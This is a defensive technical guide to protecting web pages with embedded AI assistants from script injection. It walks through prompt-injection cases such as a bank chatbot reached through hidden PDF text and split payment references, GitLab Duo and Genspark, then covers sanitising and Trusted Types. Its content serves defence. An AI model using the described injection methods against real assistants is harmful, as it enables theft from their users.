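# Defending web pages that embed AI assistants against script injection

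## How an assistant is built into a web page and what the browser separates

An embedded AI assistant is a chat program that a website places in its pages. The visitor types a question in plain language, and a large language model (a program trained on large amounts of text to generate text) writes the answer. Many assistants also have tools, which are functions the model can call to fetch data or take an action, such as looking up an order or adding a payee to a bank account. On a signed-in page, the assistant therefore works with the user's private data and authority, so an attacker who can steer it can exploit some of both.

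Such assistants are common on ordinary sites. In *When AI Meets the Web*, Kaya, Landerer and colleagues (2025) searched a public archive of the web for 17 ready-made chatbot plugins. They found 10,417 sites with one in August 2024 and 17,474 in April 2025. Only 125 of 200 sites in a spot check had a chatbot that answered, but the count leaves out the larger commercial support platforms.

### From the question to the reply

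For example, a customer signed in to a bank's website might ask the assistant whether last month's rent went out. The bank's server sends the page as HTML, the markup language of the web. The browser uses the HTML to build the DOM (Document Object Model), a live model of the page that scripts can read and change. The DOM includes the chat box, the earlier messages and the account balance next to them. When the customer presses Enter, a script in the page reads the text from the chat box and sends it to a server in an HTTP request.

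The request has to identify the customer, because HTTP keeps no record of earlier requests. Sites usually do this with a cookie, a small piece of data that the server gives the browser to store and send back. MDN's *Using HTTP cookies*, part of a reference work for web developers, describes the usual sign-in. The user sends a password, and the server checks it and replies with a cookie that holds a session ID, which identifies this period of signed-in use (the session). The browser returns the cookie with later requests, and each time the server checks that the ID is still valid. A server can mark the cookie HttpOnly, which stops scripts from reading it. But the browser still attaches the cookie to requests that the page's scripts send to the site, so a script can act within the session without reading the ID.

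With the WordPress plugins that Kaya and colleagues examined, the site's own server forwards the visitor's question to the company that runs the model. With the general-purpose commercial plugins, the visitor's browser sends the question to the plugin maker's server, which passes it on. In both cases, the model receives a single block of text containing the developer's standing instructions (the system prompt), the conversation so far, any documents the server has looked up, and the new question.

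Some plugins store the conversation history on a server or leave it with the model's provider. Eight of the 17 plugins, used on about 8,000 sites, had the visitor's browser send some or all of the history with each question and did not check whether it had been altered. A visitor could therefore add fake messages, including ones labeled as the developer's instructions. The most widely used plugin has since received fixes.

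If the answer requires data, the model outputs the name of a tool and the values to call it with, such as a payment search and a range of dates. Ordinary code runs the tool and returns the result to the model as more text, and this may repeat several times. That code usually runs on the server, but some tools run in the browser. *ChatKit.js*, OpenAI's documentation for a ready-made chat component, lists "client tool calls" among its features.

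The finished reply then returns to the browser, where a script writes it into the DOM as a new message. A reply can contain HTML as well as text, so this step matters as much for security as the earlier ones. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026), in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, argue that the model usually carries an attacker's influence to older components, such as a database or the code that draws the page, rather than adding a new low-level flaw. The damage follows if those components trust the model's output.

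### Origins, sites and cookies

A browser may have the bank's page open in one tab and a hostile page in another. It keeps them apart by origin, which is the scheme, host and port of a web address taken together. A site is a broader unit: the scheme plus the registrable domain, roughly the part of the name that somebody has to register. web.dev's *"Same-site" and "same-origin"*, a guide for developers, works through pairs of addresses to show the difference. For a page at `https://www.example.com/account`, three comparisons cover most of what matters:

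| Other address | Same origin? | Same site? |
|---|---|---|
| `https://www.example.com/help` | Yes; the path does not count | Yes |
| `https://chat.example.com` | No; the host differs | Yes |
| `http://www.example.com` | No; the scheme differs | No; the scheme counts here too |

The browser's same-origin policy prevents code from one origin from reading another origin's data or page contents. It restricts reading far more than embedding. web.dev's *Same-origin policy* explains that a page may generally display an image or a frame from a different origin, but its scripts cannot read the image's data or the document inside the frame. The details vary between browser functions, and *Same Origin Policy*, from the web's main standards body, W3C, states that no single such policy exists.

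Cookies follow a looser boundary than origins. According to MDN, a server can set a cookie's Domain attribute so that the browser also sends the cookie to every subdomain. `chat.example.com` then receives the main site's session cookie, even though its scripts cannot read the main site's pages. Moving an assistant to a subdomain therefore gives it a separate origin but not necessarily a separate session. If the server omits the attribute, the browser sends the cookie only to the host that set it.

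Script files are the great exception to the separation. A script takes on the origin of the page that loads it, whatever address the file came from. Medley and West, in *Content security policy*, give the example of a Google button on their own page: the code comes from a Google address but runs with the rights of the page around it. The browser has no way to tell that code from something an attacker slipped in. Two pieces of code that run in one page under one origin are in the same context, and each has the powers of the other. (Content Security Policy, the subject of their guide, lets a site restrict which scripts run at all.)

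A typical web page contains a lot of third-party code and content. *What It Is, Not What It Says* (Iqbal, 2026) cites measurements showing third parties on 92% of web pages, with a median of 66 per site among the top thousand sites. Iqbal also traced which script had created or changed each element on 1,270 real pages. The browser's standard attribution credited 58.7% of the third-party elements to the site itself.

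### Script injection and prompt injection

Script injection, usually called cross-site scripting or XSS, means getting attacker-written JavaScript to run as part of a site's own page. According to MDN's *Cross-site scripting (XSS)*, this requires the site to accept input that an attacker could have written and put it into a page without making sure that it cannot run as code. The same-origin policy doesn't protect the page from the injected script, because the script has the site's origin.

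MITRE's *CWE-79*, the entry for this flaw in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, distinguishes three forms by the route the code takes:

- **Stored.** The server saves the attacker's text and later includes it in a page. At the bank, this could be a payment reference that contains markup and appears in the recipient's account history.
- **Reflected.** The server copies something out of a request straight into its response. The victim follows a link with markup in the search term, and the results page repeats the term.
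- **DOM-based.** A script already in the page inserts the text into the DOM as live markup. The HTML that the server sent may have been harmless.

The route makes no difference to the harm. Once the code runs, it can do what the site's own code can do.

In prompt injection, an attacker gets a language model to read text that it then follows as an instruction. No code has to run. In direct prompt injection, the attacker types the text into the chat. In indirect prompt injection, the text is inside something the model reads on another person's behalf, such as a product review, an email or the result of a tool call. *Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes prompt injection, which depends on the meaning of sentences, from XSS, which depends on the syntax of code. Iqbal notes that a sanitiser, which removes the parts of a piece of HTML that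 could run script, therefore has nothing to remove from a plain English sentence.

The two attacks also differ in reliability and reach. A browser runs injected JavaScript like any other script, but injected prompts work only some of the time. In the tests by Kaya and colleagues, they got chatbots to do unauthorised tasks, such as writing program code, in 0–25% of cases when the plugin kept the developer's messages properly separate from other text, and in 25–100% when it did not. An injected prompt also limits the attacker to what the model can do, which is call its tools and write a reply. A script in the host page can access the whole page, including the chat window if that is part of the page.

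Each attack can lead to the other. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a demonstration against the DeepSeek chatbot in which a prompt got the model to decode a disguised string into HTML. The chat page displayed the result as live markup, which let the script inside it run and gave it access to the user's stored login token. Conversely, a script in the page can fill in the chat box or send its own request to the chat server. The model then receives the attacker's words as a user message rather than as text from an outside document, with little to mark them as untrusted.

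A lasting version of the attack may not require a script in the page. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe an attack in which a hostile site makes the victim's browser send a forged request to an assistant's memory store. The request carries the victim's cookie, the server saves the attacker's text, and the model reads it in a later conversation. They built the scenario by analogy with known attacks and do not report a real case.

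### Where the assistant's code runs

How much an injected script can reach depends on where the site has put the assistant. In the simplest arrangement, the assistant's code runs directly in the host page, the page that embeds it. Microsoft's *Publish an agent to a live or demo website* gives a complete example for Copilot Studio. The page loads a chat library from a Microsoft address, fetches a token that opens a conversation, and draws the chat into an element of its DOM. The assistant therefore shares a context with the site's own code, its analytics and advertising scripts, and anything an attacker injects. The guide calls the sample an "iframe code snippet", but the code contains no iframe, so a developer who relied on that description would wrongly assume there was a boundary between the chat and the rest of the page.

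An iframe, or frame, is a separate document shown inside the page. If it comes from another origin, the browser stops scripts in the host page from reading the conversation in it, and scripts in the frame from reading the host page. Only code in the frame's own document shares a context with the assistant, including any script that a badly handled reply injects there. A frame from the host page's own origin gives no such protection unless the site sandboxes it, which makes the browser restrict what the frame can do.

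Copilot Studio also offers a frame of this kind. Microsoft's *Every Path to Integrating Your Copilot Studio Agent* says that a user's existing sign-in to the site does not carry over to the frame, so the user has to copy a validation code from another browser tab. For smooth sign-in, the guide recommends that sites host the chat library themselves, which is the weaker arrangement.

OpenAI's ChatKit also draws its chat in a frame that OpenAI hosts, regardless of who runs the chat server. OpenAI's *ChatKit* documentation describes a hosted version in which the site's server authenticates the user and obtains a short-lived client secret, and a script in the host page fetches the secret and passes it to the chat component. (OpenAI scheduled Agent Builder, the service behind that version, to shut down on November 30, 2026, but ChatKit continues.) An injected script could not read such a frame,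 but it would run in the same page as the code that sets up the chat, and it could cover or replace the frame.

An assistant can also run outside the page, either in a browser extension (an add-on that the user installs), as with Anthropic's Claude in Chrome, or in the browser itself, as in Perplexity's Comet. These assistants read pages, click, and fill in forms, often across several sites where the user is signed in. Some accept commands from websites. An extension can list the sites whose pages may send it messages, and a draft standard called WebMCP lets a page register tools with the browser for an assistant to call.

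An assistant of this sort shares no context with code in the page. Extensions run their scripts in an "isolated world", whose variables the page's scripts cannot access. The weak point is the channel through which the website sends the assistant instructions. *WebMCP-Phalanx* (Lee, Chang and colleagues, 2026) examined WebMCP and found that a site's main program and its advertising and analytics scripts all have access to one tool list. Without added protection, every attempt by one script to remove or overwrite another's tools succeeded. The paper's remedy stopped those attacks, but the browser could still identify only the origin that had registered a tool, not the script. An assistant that accepts instructions from a trusted site will therefore accept them from any code running in that site's pages.

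In all these arrangements, the attacker can place text or markup where the page or the model will process it, but controls neither the site's server nor the user's machine. The attacker could use a customer review, a support ticket, or a link that the victim opens. Kaya and colleagues found that 15 of the 17 plugins they studied can scrape web pages for the chatbot to use, without separating the site's own text from its visitors'. About 13% of the online shops they checked by hand had already exposed their chatbots to third-party content.

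Other threat models make different assumptions about the attacker. Lee and colleagues assume that an attacker has already compromised an advertising or analytics script on the page. Iqbal, who studies assistants that browse on the user's behalf, excludes attackers who can reach their goal with their own scripts, because they do not need the assistant. For an embedded assistant, that excluded case is the most serious one, since the attacker's target may be the conversation and the tools themselves.

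## How the assistant's own replies bring script into the page

An assistant's reply may contain text from anyone whose writing the model has processed. Developers can easily treat the reply as the site's own text because it comes from a server the site chose. If a reply contains an attacker's markup and the page inserts it as live HTML, any script in that markup runs with the site's origin.

Websites usually make outside text safe by encoding it. Before adding a customer's name to a page, for example, the site replaces characters such as angle brackets with codes that the browser displays as those characters but does not treat as markup. This works when the developer knows which fields hold text from outsiders, but a model's reply mixes text from many sources without marking where each part came from. Encoding the whole reply can also break its formatting. Many assistants write in Markdown,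 a simple notation for links, lists and bold text that the page converts to HTML, and encoding that HTML would make the browser show the tags instead of the formatting. Markdown also permits raw HTML tags, and some converters let them through.

Sometimes the model only has to repeat markup. In Embrace The Red's *DeepSeek AI*, a researcher asked the DeepSeek chatbot for a list of strings used to test for XSS, and the chat page ran code from the list it returned. A model can also decode markup from a disguised string, as in the later DeepSeek demonstration, or assemble it from harmless fragments. In either case, a filter on incoming text finds no tag because the model has not yet written it.

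Singh and colleagues note that structured output, in which the model fills in fixed fields instead of writing freely, reduces the risk. The page must still treat each field as text, since a field meant for a name can hold an HTML tag.

### The bank case of August 2026

Positive Security's *Banking AI XSS* (2026) reports a flaw of this kind at the security firm's own business bank, which it does not name. The bank's assistant could look up customer data and take actions, including adding a payee.

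The researcher first asked the bank's chatbot to add a payee with an ordinary made-up name, then one whose name was an image tag. The reply repeated the name, and the browser drew a broken image in its place, so the page was inserting replies as live HTML. A sanitiser might still have been removing anything that could run script. To check, the researcher added an invented event handler, an attribute that makes the browser run script when something happens to an element, and the page kept it. An unidentified safeguard blocked a request with the best-known real handler, but a rarer one from a public list worked. The researcher had script running in the bank's page within two minutes of first using the chatbot.

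A longer payee name loaded a script file from the researcher's server. This worked less reliably because more complicated names more often came back with their angle brackets encoded. Starting the name with a plain image tag seemed to help the rest come through as markup. The loaded script used the signed-in session to request the account's email address from the bank, then sent it to an outside server. The bank's page had no Content Security Policy to restrict where scripts could come from or where they could send data. According to Positive Security, only the bank's second-factor check still prevented such a script from taking the money in the account.

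At this stage, an attacker would have had to persuade customers to paste the markup into their own chats, so the firm looked for ways to get it to the model from outside.

The first was a PDF invoice in which the researcher had hidden the markup as white text on a white background. If a customer uploaded it and asked the assistant to add the payee, the script would run. In the hidden text, the researcher also wrote that the name looked strange and asked the assistant to verify it. This made the model more likely to print the name in full, and was less likely to trigger the bank's safeguards against prompt injection than a direct command to include the full name.

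A bank transfer required even less of the victim, because the sender writes the payment reference and it appears in the recipient's account automatically. References in SEPA, the European system for euro payments, can hold 140 characters. They cannot include angle brackets, which would make script injection through a reference very unlikely on an ordinary account page.

Positive Security replaced the characters forbidden by the payment system with abbreviations and split the text across two transfers of one cent each. The reference on one transfer also contained instructions for the model to join the parts and decode the abbreviations. The model did so and wrote the restored tag into its reply, where the page ran it, even though the payment system's character rule had worked as intended.

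In the demonstration video of the transfer attack, the customer's own request repeats some of the attacker's instructions. The firm was working on a live account and did not want to send many suspicious transfers. The video shows that the model could rebuild markup from payment references, but it does not support the claim in the article's summary that a plain request to list the month's transactions was enough.

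Positive Security reported the flaw on July 13, 2026. The bank acknowledged it on July 15, after a reminder, and announced a fix less than three hours later. In a quick retest, the replies seemed to always arrive encoded.

One person can put markup in an invoice or payment reference, and the script runs in another person's session when they ask the assistant about it. The bank had at first classified the flaw as "scoped only to your user", with no way to use it against other customers, which would have been fair if customers could only type markup into their own chat. It corrected its assessment after the firm explained the other route.

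Encoding the assistant's replies keeps them from injecting script into the page, but it doesn't stop prompt injection. Blue41, a company that sells monitoring for AI assistants, tested another European bank's assistant with a two-cent transfer. The transfer's description got the assistant to show the customer a phishing message disguised as a request from the bank to sign in again, without any script running. That bank also had filters, but they missed the text because it looked too much like ordinary transaction data.

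### Replies displayed before they are complete

Many chat pages display a reply piece by piece as the model writes it. This can defeat a filter that would have handled the finished reply correctly.

Duo, the assistant on the software hosting service GitLab, had this problem. Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft* explains that an attacker could hide instructions in a public project's source code, comments or commit messages (notes on code changes). Duo read them when another user asked about the project. Duo's replies were converted from Markdown to HTML line by line, before the structure of the whole reply was known. A tag inside a code block should appear as plain text, but if it arrived before the page had recognised the block, the page could treat it as live HTML.

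Duo also passed its replies through DOMPurify, a widely used sanitiser, which removed script but left images, forms and links in place. Researchers at Legit Security could therefore inject HTML but not run JavaScript. The injected HTML was enough to leak private source code through an image's address. Legit Security reported the problem in February 2025, and GitLab stopped Duo from displaying images and forms that point to outside domains.

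Microsoft 365 Copilot had a similar fault more than a year later. According to Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026), Copilot's search page neutralised markup by wrapping the reply in a code block, but only once the model had finished. Until then, the browser treated the tags as live and requested an attacker's image. The code block changed what the user saw, but the browser had already sent the request. To start the attack, the victim only had to click a link to a genuine Microsoft address that contained the attacker's prompt. Microsoft has fixed the flaw.

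Varonis' experiment leaked data through an image and did not run script. A tag that ran script would have the same timing problem, unless another layer removed the tag. Varonis recommends cleaning the output when the page displays it. For a streamed reply, that means cleaning it every time the page adds to it.

### Replies that someone else opens

A script in a saved reply can also run again when someone reopens the conversation. Genspark, an AI chat service, saved conversations and let users share them by link. In *Wormable Stored XSS in Genspark AI Chat*, the researcher vuvannam12082005 asked the model to repeat a line of markup exactly, without putting it in a code block. The page ran the script when the reply appeared, again after a reload, and again when the researcher opened the shared link in a private browser window.

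The attacker types the prompt, and anyone who opens the link is a victim. The bank's first reasoning would not have covered this attack either. The script could show a visitor a false login form or read any session cookie the site had left accessible to scripts. The title calls the flaw "wormable", but the published test shows a saved script reaching each person who follows the link, not code that copies itself into new conversations. Genspark deployed a fix in the second half of December 2025, within about two weeks of the report.

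A customer service chatbot's replies can also reach the support agent who takes over when the bot cannot help. In September 2025, researchers at the news site Cybernews reported that they had got the chatbot on the website of Yellow.ai, which sells chatbots to other companies, to produce HTML containing script. According to SC Media's *Yellow.ai chatbot vulnerability puts cookies at risk*, an attacker could then ask for a human, and the saved reply would run in the agent's browser when the agent opened the conversation. The script could take the agent's session cookie, which could give the attacker access to the support system and the other customers' data it holds.

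The extent of the flaw is disputed. SC Media described it as a flaw in a product used by Sony, Domino's and Hyundai. Willing (2025), in *Yellow.ai’s Own Chatbot Got Tricked Into Generating Malicious Code, Reports*, noted that the researchers did not know whether clients' chatbots were exposed. Yellow.ai later replied that the attack had worked only on an experimental demonstration widget on its corporate website, and that its production systems have different security settings. The company had fixed the widget by cleaning the generated code.

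Cybernews had found the same route in Lenovo's support chatbot shortly before. Lenovo confirmed to SC Media UK that a researcher had told it about an XSS flaw. The bank's assistant may have had this weakness too, since it automatically forwarded one of Positive Security's test conversations to a human agent. Positive Security did not test whether the markup ran on the agent's screen.

### A model server that sends code

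In the cases so far, the page wrongly treated text as markup, but Open WebUI, a chat interface that organisations run on their own servers, accepted code outright. Its Direct Connections feature lets a user connect the interface to an outside model server. *Vulnerability Discovered in Open WebUI Enables Account Takeover and Remote Code Execution* (Simonovich, 2026) describes what a hostile server could do through this feature.

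The server sends its reply as a stream of small messages called events. Most carry pieces of text, but Open WebUI also recognised an "execute" event, whose contents the page ran as JavaScript in its own origin. An attacker who controlled the server could therefore answer any message from the user with code, without having to trick a model or get a tag past a sanitiser.

That code could read the user's login token, because Open WebUI kept it in localStorage, browser storage that every script in the page can read. With the token, an attacker could take over the account and read its chats and uploaded documents. Some users also had permission to create tools, which the Open WebUI server ran as Python programs without a sandbox. A token stolen from one of these users gave the attacker control of the server.

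The flaw was harder to exploit than these consequences suggest, because Direct Connections is off by default and the victim had to add the attacker's server address. The public CVE record, *Open WebUI Affected by an External Model Server (Direct Connections) Code Injection* (2025), lists it as CVE-2025-64496, with a severity of 7.3 out of 10. An assessment added to the record in November 2025 lists a proof of concept but no active attacks. After an incomplete first patch, version 0.6.35 blocked "execute" events from these connections.

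### What researchers have measured

These cases show that the routes exist, but not how often an attempt succeeds. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian treat script injection through a model as its own category, but they did not test it and cite the DeepSeek demonstration as evidence. They say the same mechanism could also produce stored or DOM-based XSS, and leave the experiments to future work.

They instead tested server-side request forgery, in which an attacker gets a server to send requests to addresses the attacker cannot reach. They built a concert ticket assistant with a tool that would fetch any web address, and tried five attacks on seven models, ten times each. Without protective instructions, Llama 3.3 70B carried out every request the attacker typed into the chat, while GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4.6 carried out none.

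The researchers then told the models which addresses were allowed. This stopped all the attacks typed into the chat, but not all those hidden in a stored concert review. Llama's failures on the hidden attack rose from six in ten attempts to all ten, while GPT-oss 120B's fell from five to zero. The comparison is imperfect because the researchers also changed the hidden text to include a claim that the list of allowed addresses had been extended. The ten attempts also took place in one conversation, so earlier answers could affect later ones.

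These figures are weak evidence of how often a model will produce working markup, but they show that the result can depend heavily on the model. This fits the Genspark report, whose author used Gemini 3 Pro and considered Claude models less likely to comply. Switching models may therefore change a site's exposure, even if the page stays the same. As a defence against script injection, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recommend that the application encode or sanitise every reply before displaying it, regardless of the model's instructions.

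### Routes that do not pass through the model

Even handling replies perfectly does not protect the rest of the page. Chat software also has ordinary XSS flaws, some of which involve what the visitor sends. AI Engine, a WordPress plugin, displayed visitors' messages on a screen where administrators review conversations. In an answer to the forum user wpmakenorg, the plugin's author explained that a visitor could leave a message containing HTML and the screen would render it as live markup (CVE-2026-65545). The screen's filter recognised only lowercase tag names, but browsers accept either case. The author has released a fix.

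Uploaded files can also carry script into the page. According to INCIBE's *CVE-2025-8349* (2025), an attacker could upload a PDF containing JavaScript through the Tawk Live Chat widget, and the script ran when another user viewed the file. The flaw was in how the application displayed the file, whereas the attack on the bank required its model to read the PDF and repeat its contents.

Such a flaw can do more harm when a chat widget is embedded in another site's page. The GitLab Advisory Database describes one in the viewer of Typebot, a chatbot builder (CVE-2026-39964). Sites usually embed the viewer in their own pages, so the attacker's script runs in the host page's origin and can take session tokens. The flaw may also be in a component that has little to do with chat. An attack on ChatGPT that Willison (2026) summarised in October started from a library for entering mathematics.

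An attacker can also alter a script that the site loads on purpose. ThaiCERT's *Supply Chain Attack via CDN Affects Popular WordPress Plugins* (2026) reports that attackers changed files on the content delivery network of Awesome Motive, which makes the OptinMonster, TrustPulse and PushEngage plugins used by more than 1.2 million sites. When the altered code detected a signed-in WordPress administrator, it tried to create another administrator account and install a plugin with a back door. The attack did not require a malicious file on the site's own server beforehand.

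In another case, attackers hijacked the domain that serves AppsFlyer's analytics code instead of altering the company's files, according to an analysis by cside, which monitors third-party scripts. Thousands of websites received a cryptocurrency-stealing script from what looked like the usual source. The script watched the DOM and replaced `fetch`, the browser function that pages use to send requests. On a page with an assistant, the same function may carry the user's questions and the model's replies.

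## Cleaning HTML and guarding the functions that insert it

A chat page usually turns a model's Markdown reply into live content in four steps. The reply arrives as text, a converter changes the Markdown into a string of HTML, a sanitiser removes anything that could run script, and the page inserts what is left into the DOM. Different defences act at different steps:

| Step | What the page has | Defence that can act here |
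|---|---|---|
| Reply arrives | Markdown text | Inserting it as plain text, which makes the later steps unnecessary |
| Conversion | HTML string | A converter setting that refuses raw HTML tags |
| Sanitising | HTML string | A sanitiser such as DOMPurify |
| Insertion | Live elements | `setHTML`, which cleans the HTML as it inserts it, and Trusted Types, which blocks strings that skipped the site's policy |

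Sanitising has to come after Markdown is converted to HTML, because the conversion can turn text without tags into dangerous HTML. A Markdown link is a label in square brackets followed by an address in parentheses. If the address starts with `javascript:`, the browser runs the rest as code when the user clicks the link. A sanitiser run before conversion would treat the link as ordinary text, but one run afterwards can check its address. The page should also not edit the HTML after sanitising it, for example to colour code samples, since the edit could add markup that hasn't been sanitised.

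Google's *Best practices to render streamed LLM responses* (Chrome for Developers, 2025) rightly recommends treating a model's output like text from an unknown user, but its sample code does the cleaning in the wrong order. The code runs DOMPurify on the Markdown and then passes the original Markdown to the converter, so the safety of links depends on the converter. It would also cut off a harmless reply that explained script tags in a code block, because DOMPurify would find a tag to remove.

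### Showing the reply as text

Output encoding turns an opening angle bracket into `&lt;`, so any tags in a reply appear as text. A script in the page can get the same result by passing the reply to the `append()` method, which adds a string as text and never parses it as HTML. Chrome for Developers recommends `append()` for unformatted replies, partly because it is fast.

The right encoding depends on where the text goes. Encoding angle brackets does not make a `javascript:` address safe as a link target, because the address can run a script without them. *Trust Me If You Can* (Roth, Gröber and colleagues, 2024) gives the example of React, a popular library for building pages, which encoded ordinary strings automatically but still allowed `javascript:` addresses in links.

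### Allowlists and blocklists

A page that needs bold text, lists and links has to let some HTML through. DOMPurify parses the HTML string into a tree of elements, removes every element and attribute not on its allowlist, and writes the rest back as a string.

A blocklist specifies what to remove. HTML has many event handlers, and an attacker needs only one that the list omits, like the rarer handler that worked at the bank. An allowlist removes any handler that isn't on it, including those its author has never heard of.

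Roth and colleagues asked 13 web developers to protect a small application that contained Twitter and Facebook widgets. Most of those who wrote their own HTML filter started from an example that encoded every opening angle bracket. This broke the widgets, and two developers then switched to a blocklist that removed only the start of script tags, which left event handlers working. Every home-made filter was easy to bypass, and only seven of the 13 developers ended up with a secure HTML sanitiser. The paper also cites Klein and colleagues, who found 88 bypassable sanitisers in use on 102 domains.

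### Mutation attacks

Even a good allowlist can fail if the browser parses the cleaned HTML differently from the sanitiser. Browsers repair broken HTML, and the repair depends on where the HTML is inserted. web.dev's *Safe DOM manipulation with the Sanitizer API* gives the example of a table cell, which makes sense inside a table but not inside a `div`. DOMPurify receives only a string, so it has to assume where the HTML will be inserted.

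Braun, in *Why the Sanitizer API is just setHTML()*, traces the problem to parsing the HTML twice. Braun manages application security for Firefox and helped write the specification for the browser's own sanitiser. When a page uses DOMPurify with `innerHTML`, the usual function for inserting HTML, the following happens:

1. DOMPurify parses the string, usually as the body of a new, empty document.
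2. It removes the unwanted elements and attributes.
3. It turns the remaining tree back into a string.
4. `innerHTML` parses that string again, this time as the contents of the chat box.
5. The browser inserts the new elements into the page.

In a mutation attack, the attacker writes markup that is harmless when DOMPurify parses it but changes meaning when it is parsed again through `innerHTML`. For example, text that was part of an attribute can become a tag. WHATWG's *Dynamic markup insertion*, a chapter of the HTML standard, lists wrongly nested tags and "foreign content", such as SVG drawings inside HTML, as ways to cause this.

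The standard therefore tells developers to treat a cleaned tree as untrusted again once they have turned it back into a string. A chat page that stores the cleaned HTML of a reply has to sanitise that HTML again when the user reopens the conversation.

### Replies that arrive in pieces

Streaming makes cleaning harder because a dangerous tag can be split across two pieces of the reply, neither of which looks dangerous by itself. Chrome for Developers therefore advises joining all the pieces received so far and sanitising the whole text whenever a new piece arrives. It also recommends that the page stop displaying the reply as soon as the sanitiser removes anything.

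With `innerHTML`, the browser would also have to parse and redraw the entire reply every time a few words arrived. A streaming Markdown converter avoids this by adding only the new part. It holds back anything ambiguous, such as a single asterisk that could begin a list item, italics or bold text, but GitLab's assistant converted its replies too early.

The HTML standard now has methods for streaming. A page can send pieces of HTML to `streamHTML()` as they arrive, and the browser removes unsafe content while parsing them. Because one parser reads the whole stream, splitting a tag between two pieces does not hide it. The method accepts HTML, not Markdown, so most chat pages would still need to convert Markdown to HTML as it streams. If the converter mistook a code sample for real markup, the reply would look wrong, but `streamHTML()` would still remove any script in the sample.

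### The browser's own sanitiser

`setHTML()`, the main function in the browser's Sanitizer API, handles a complete piece of HTML. The browser parses the string once, in the context of the element that will hold it, removes what is unsafe, and replaces the element's contents with the result. Braun first wanted a function that returned a cleaned string, as DOMPurify does. `setHTML()` returns nothing, so a developer cannot parse its output again in the wrong context.

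Sites can choose which elements and attributes `setHTML()` keeps, but according to WHATWG, it must always remove markup that can run script, and a browser that lets such markup through has a bug. The default settings remove more. In an example from Mozilla's *Goodbye innerHTML, Hello setHTML*, the browser removes an image along with its event handler. Functions whose names end in "Unsafe", such as `setHTMLUnsafe()`, do no cleaning by default.

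A developer still has to use `setHTML()` everywhere. One forgotten `innerHTML` in an old library is enough to let an attacker in.

### Trusted Types

Trusted Types addresses forgotten calls by changing how the browser treats injection sinks, the functions that can turn a string into running code or live markup. Kotowicz (2021) counts about 60 of them in *Trusted Types*, a report on Google's use of the feature. MDN's *Trusted Types API* groups them by what they do with a string: `innerHTML` parses it as HTML, `eval()` runs it as JavaScript, and a script element's `src` property uses it as the address of a script to load.

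To use an HTML sink, the site's code first passes the string through a policy, which is a named set of functions that the developer writes. This policy uses DOMPurify:

```js
const replyPolicy = trustedTypes.createPolicy("assistant-reply", {
  createHTML: (html) => DOMPurify.sanitize(html),
});
box.innerHTML = replyPolicy.createHTML(html);
```

The policy returns a `TrustedHTML` object instead of a string. Only a policy can make such an object, so other code cannot label a string as trusted.

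The browser enforces the rule only if the site switches it on in its Content Security Policy, with two directives:

- `require-trusted-types-for 'script'` makes the sinks refuse plain strings.
- `trusted-types assistant-reply` lists the names of the policies that code in the page may create. Creating one with any other name causes an error.

Suppose the bank's assistant has just added a payee whose name is an image tag with an event handler. After conversion, the variable `html` holds this string, with the attacker's code left out:

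```html
<p><strong>Payee added:</strong> <img src="x" onerror="…"></p>
```

The result depends on how the page inserts the string into the chat box:

| Code in the page | Result |
|---|---|
| `box.append(html)` | The customer sees the tags as characters. |
| `box.innerHTML = html`, without enforcement | The customer sees bold text and a broken image, and the attacker's code runs. |
| `box.innerHTML = html`, with enforcement and no default policy | The browser throws a `TypeError` and inserts nothing. |
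| `box.innerHTML = replyPolicy.createHTML(html)` | The customer sees bold text and a broken image, but the handler is gone. |
| `box.setHTML(html)` | The customer sees only the bold text. |

With enforcement, an overlooked `innerHTML` assignment causes an error that developers can notice and fix, rather than an unnoticed vulnerability. Sites can start in report-only mode, as Google did, to find these assignments before the browser begins blocking them.

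A site can also create a policy named "default", and the browser will pass it any plain string that reaches a sink. This keeps old code working, but MDN recommends it only until developers have rewritten that code.

### Allowing only setHTML

A policy is only as good as its code, and Braun, in *Perfect types with setHTML()*, argues that looking after one takes constant attention from people who understand security. Braun's alternative is to forbid policies altogether:

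```
Content-Security-Policy: require-trusted-types-for 'script'; trusted-types 'none'
```

The sinks now accept only trusted objects, which nothing in the page can create, so `innerHTML` and the other old functions no longer take HTML. `setHTML()` still works because it does its own cleaning, and so does `Document.parseHTML()`, which cleans HTML and puts it into a separate document. Code can still add plain text or build elements one by one.

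The idea is older than `setHTML()`. Jun Kokatsu of Microsoft applied the same header to the Chromium browser's built-in pages, which use React to create their elements. According to Kotowicz, many React applications can enforce Trusted Types without code changes.

### Browser support in late 2026

| Feature | Chrome | Firefox | Safari |
|---|---|---|---|
| Trusted Types | 83 (May 2020) | 148 (February 2026) | 26 |
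| `setHTML()` and the Sanitizer API | 146 (March 2026) | 148 (February 2026) | Not as of June 2026 |

Sources disagree about Firefox's support for Trusted Types. According to MDN and web.dev's *February 2026 Baseline monthly digest* (2026), all major browsers have supported the feature since February 2026. Can I use's *Trusted Types for DOM manipulation* table, from spring 2026, lists it as disabled by default in Firefox 148 and later.

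Mozilla's records support the February date, so the Can I use table is probably out of date. Wang, who worked on the feature for Firefox, announced in *Intent to ship* (2025) that version 148 would turn it on by default on all platforms, and Mozilla then said that version 148 supported it. Before version 148, Firefox had enabled it only in test versions. The discussion under tschuster's *Ship Trusted Types*, Mozilla's tracking page for the work, shows that another compatibility database once listed the wrong version because its tests could not distinguish an early beta from a release.

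Web Platform DX's *Sanitizer API* lists no support for the API in Safari or Chrome. The Chrome entry is wrong, since the release notes in Chrome for Developers' *Chrome 146* (2026) include the feature. Apple's WebKit team, which makes Safari's engine, supports the proposal, according to Chromium's *Intent to Ship*.

Safari 26 enforces Trusted Types but has no `setHTML()`, so Braun's strict header would block `innerHTML` there without providing a replacement. To show formatted replies in Safari, a site needs to allow at least one named policy that cleans the HTML with DOMPurify.

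The streaming methods are newer. Chrome for Developers (2026) listed them for the Chrome 154 beta on September 2. WebKit had only an open request for them, *New HTML setting methods (stream, positional, runScripts)*, which Rosenthal (2026) filed on May 28.

Mozilla is also exploring a way to apply the browser's sanitiser automatically through Trusted Types. According to Mozilla's *Firefox Security & Privacy Newsletter 2026 Q2* (2026), sites would not have to change their application code.

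### Results at Google and in a usability study

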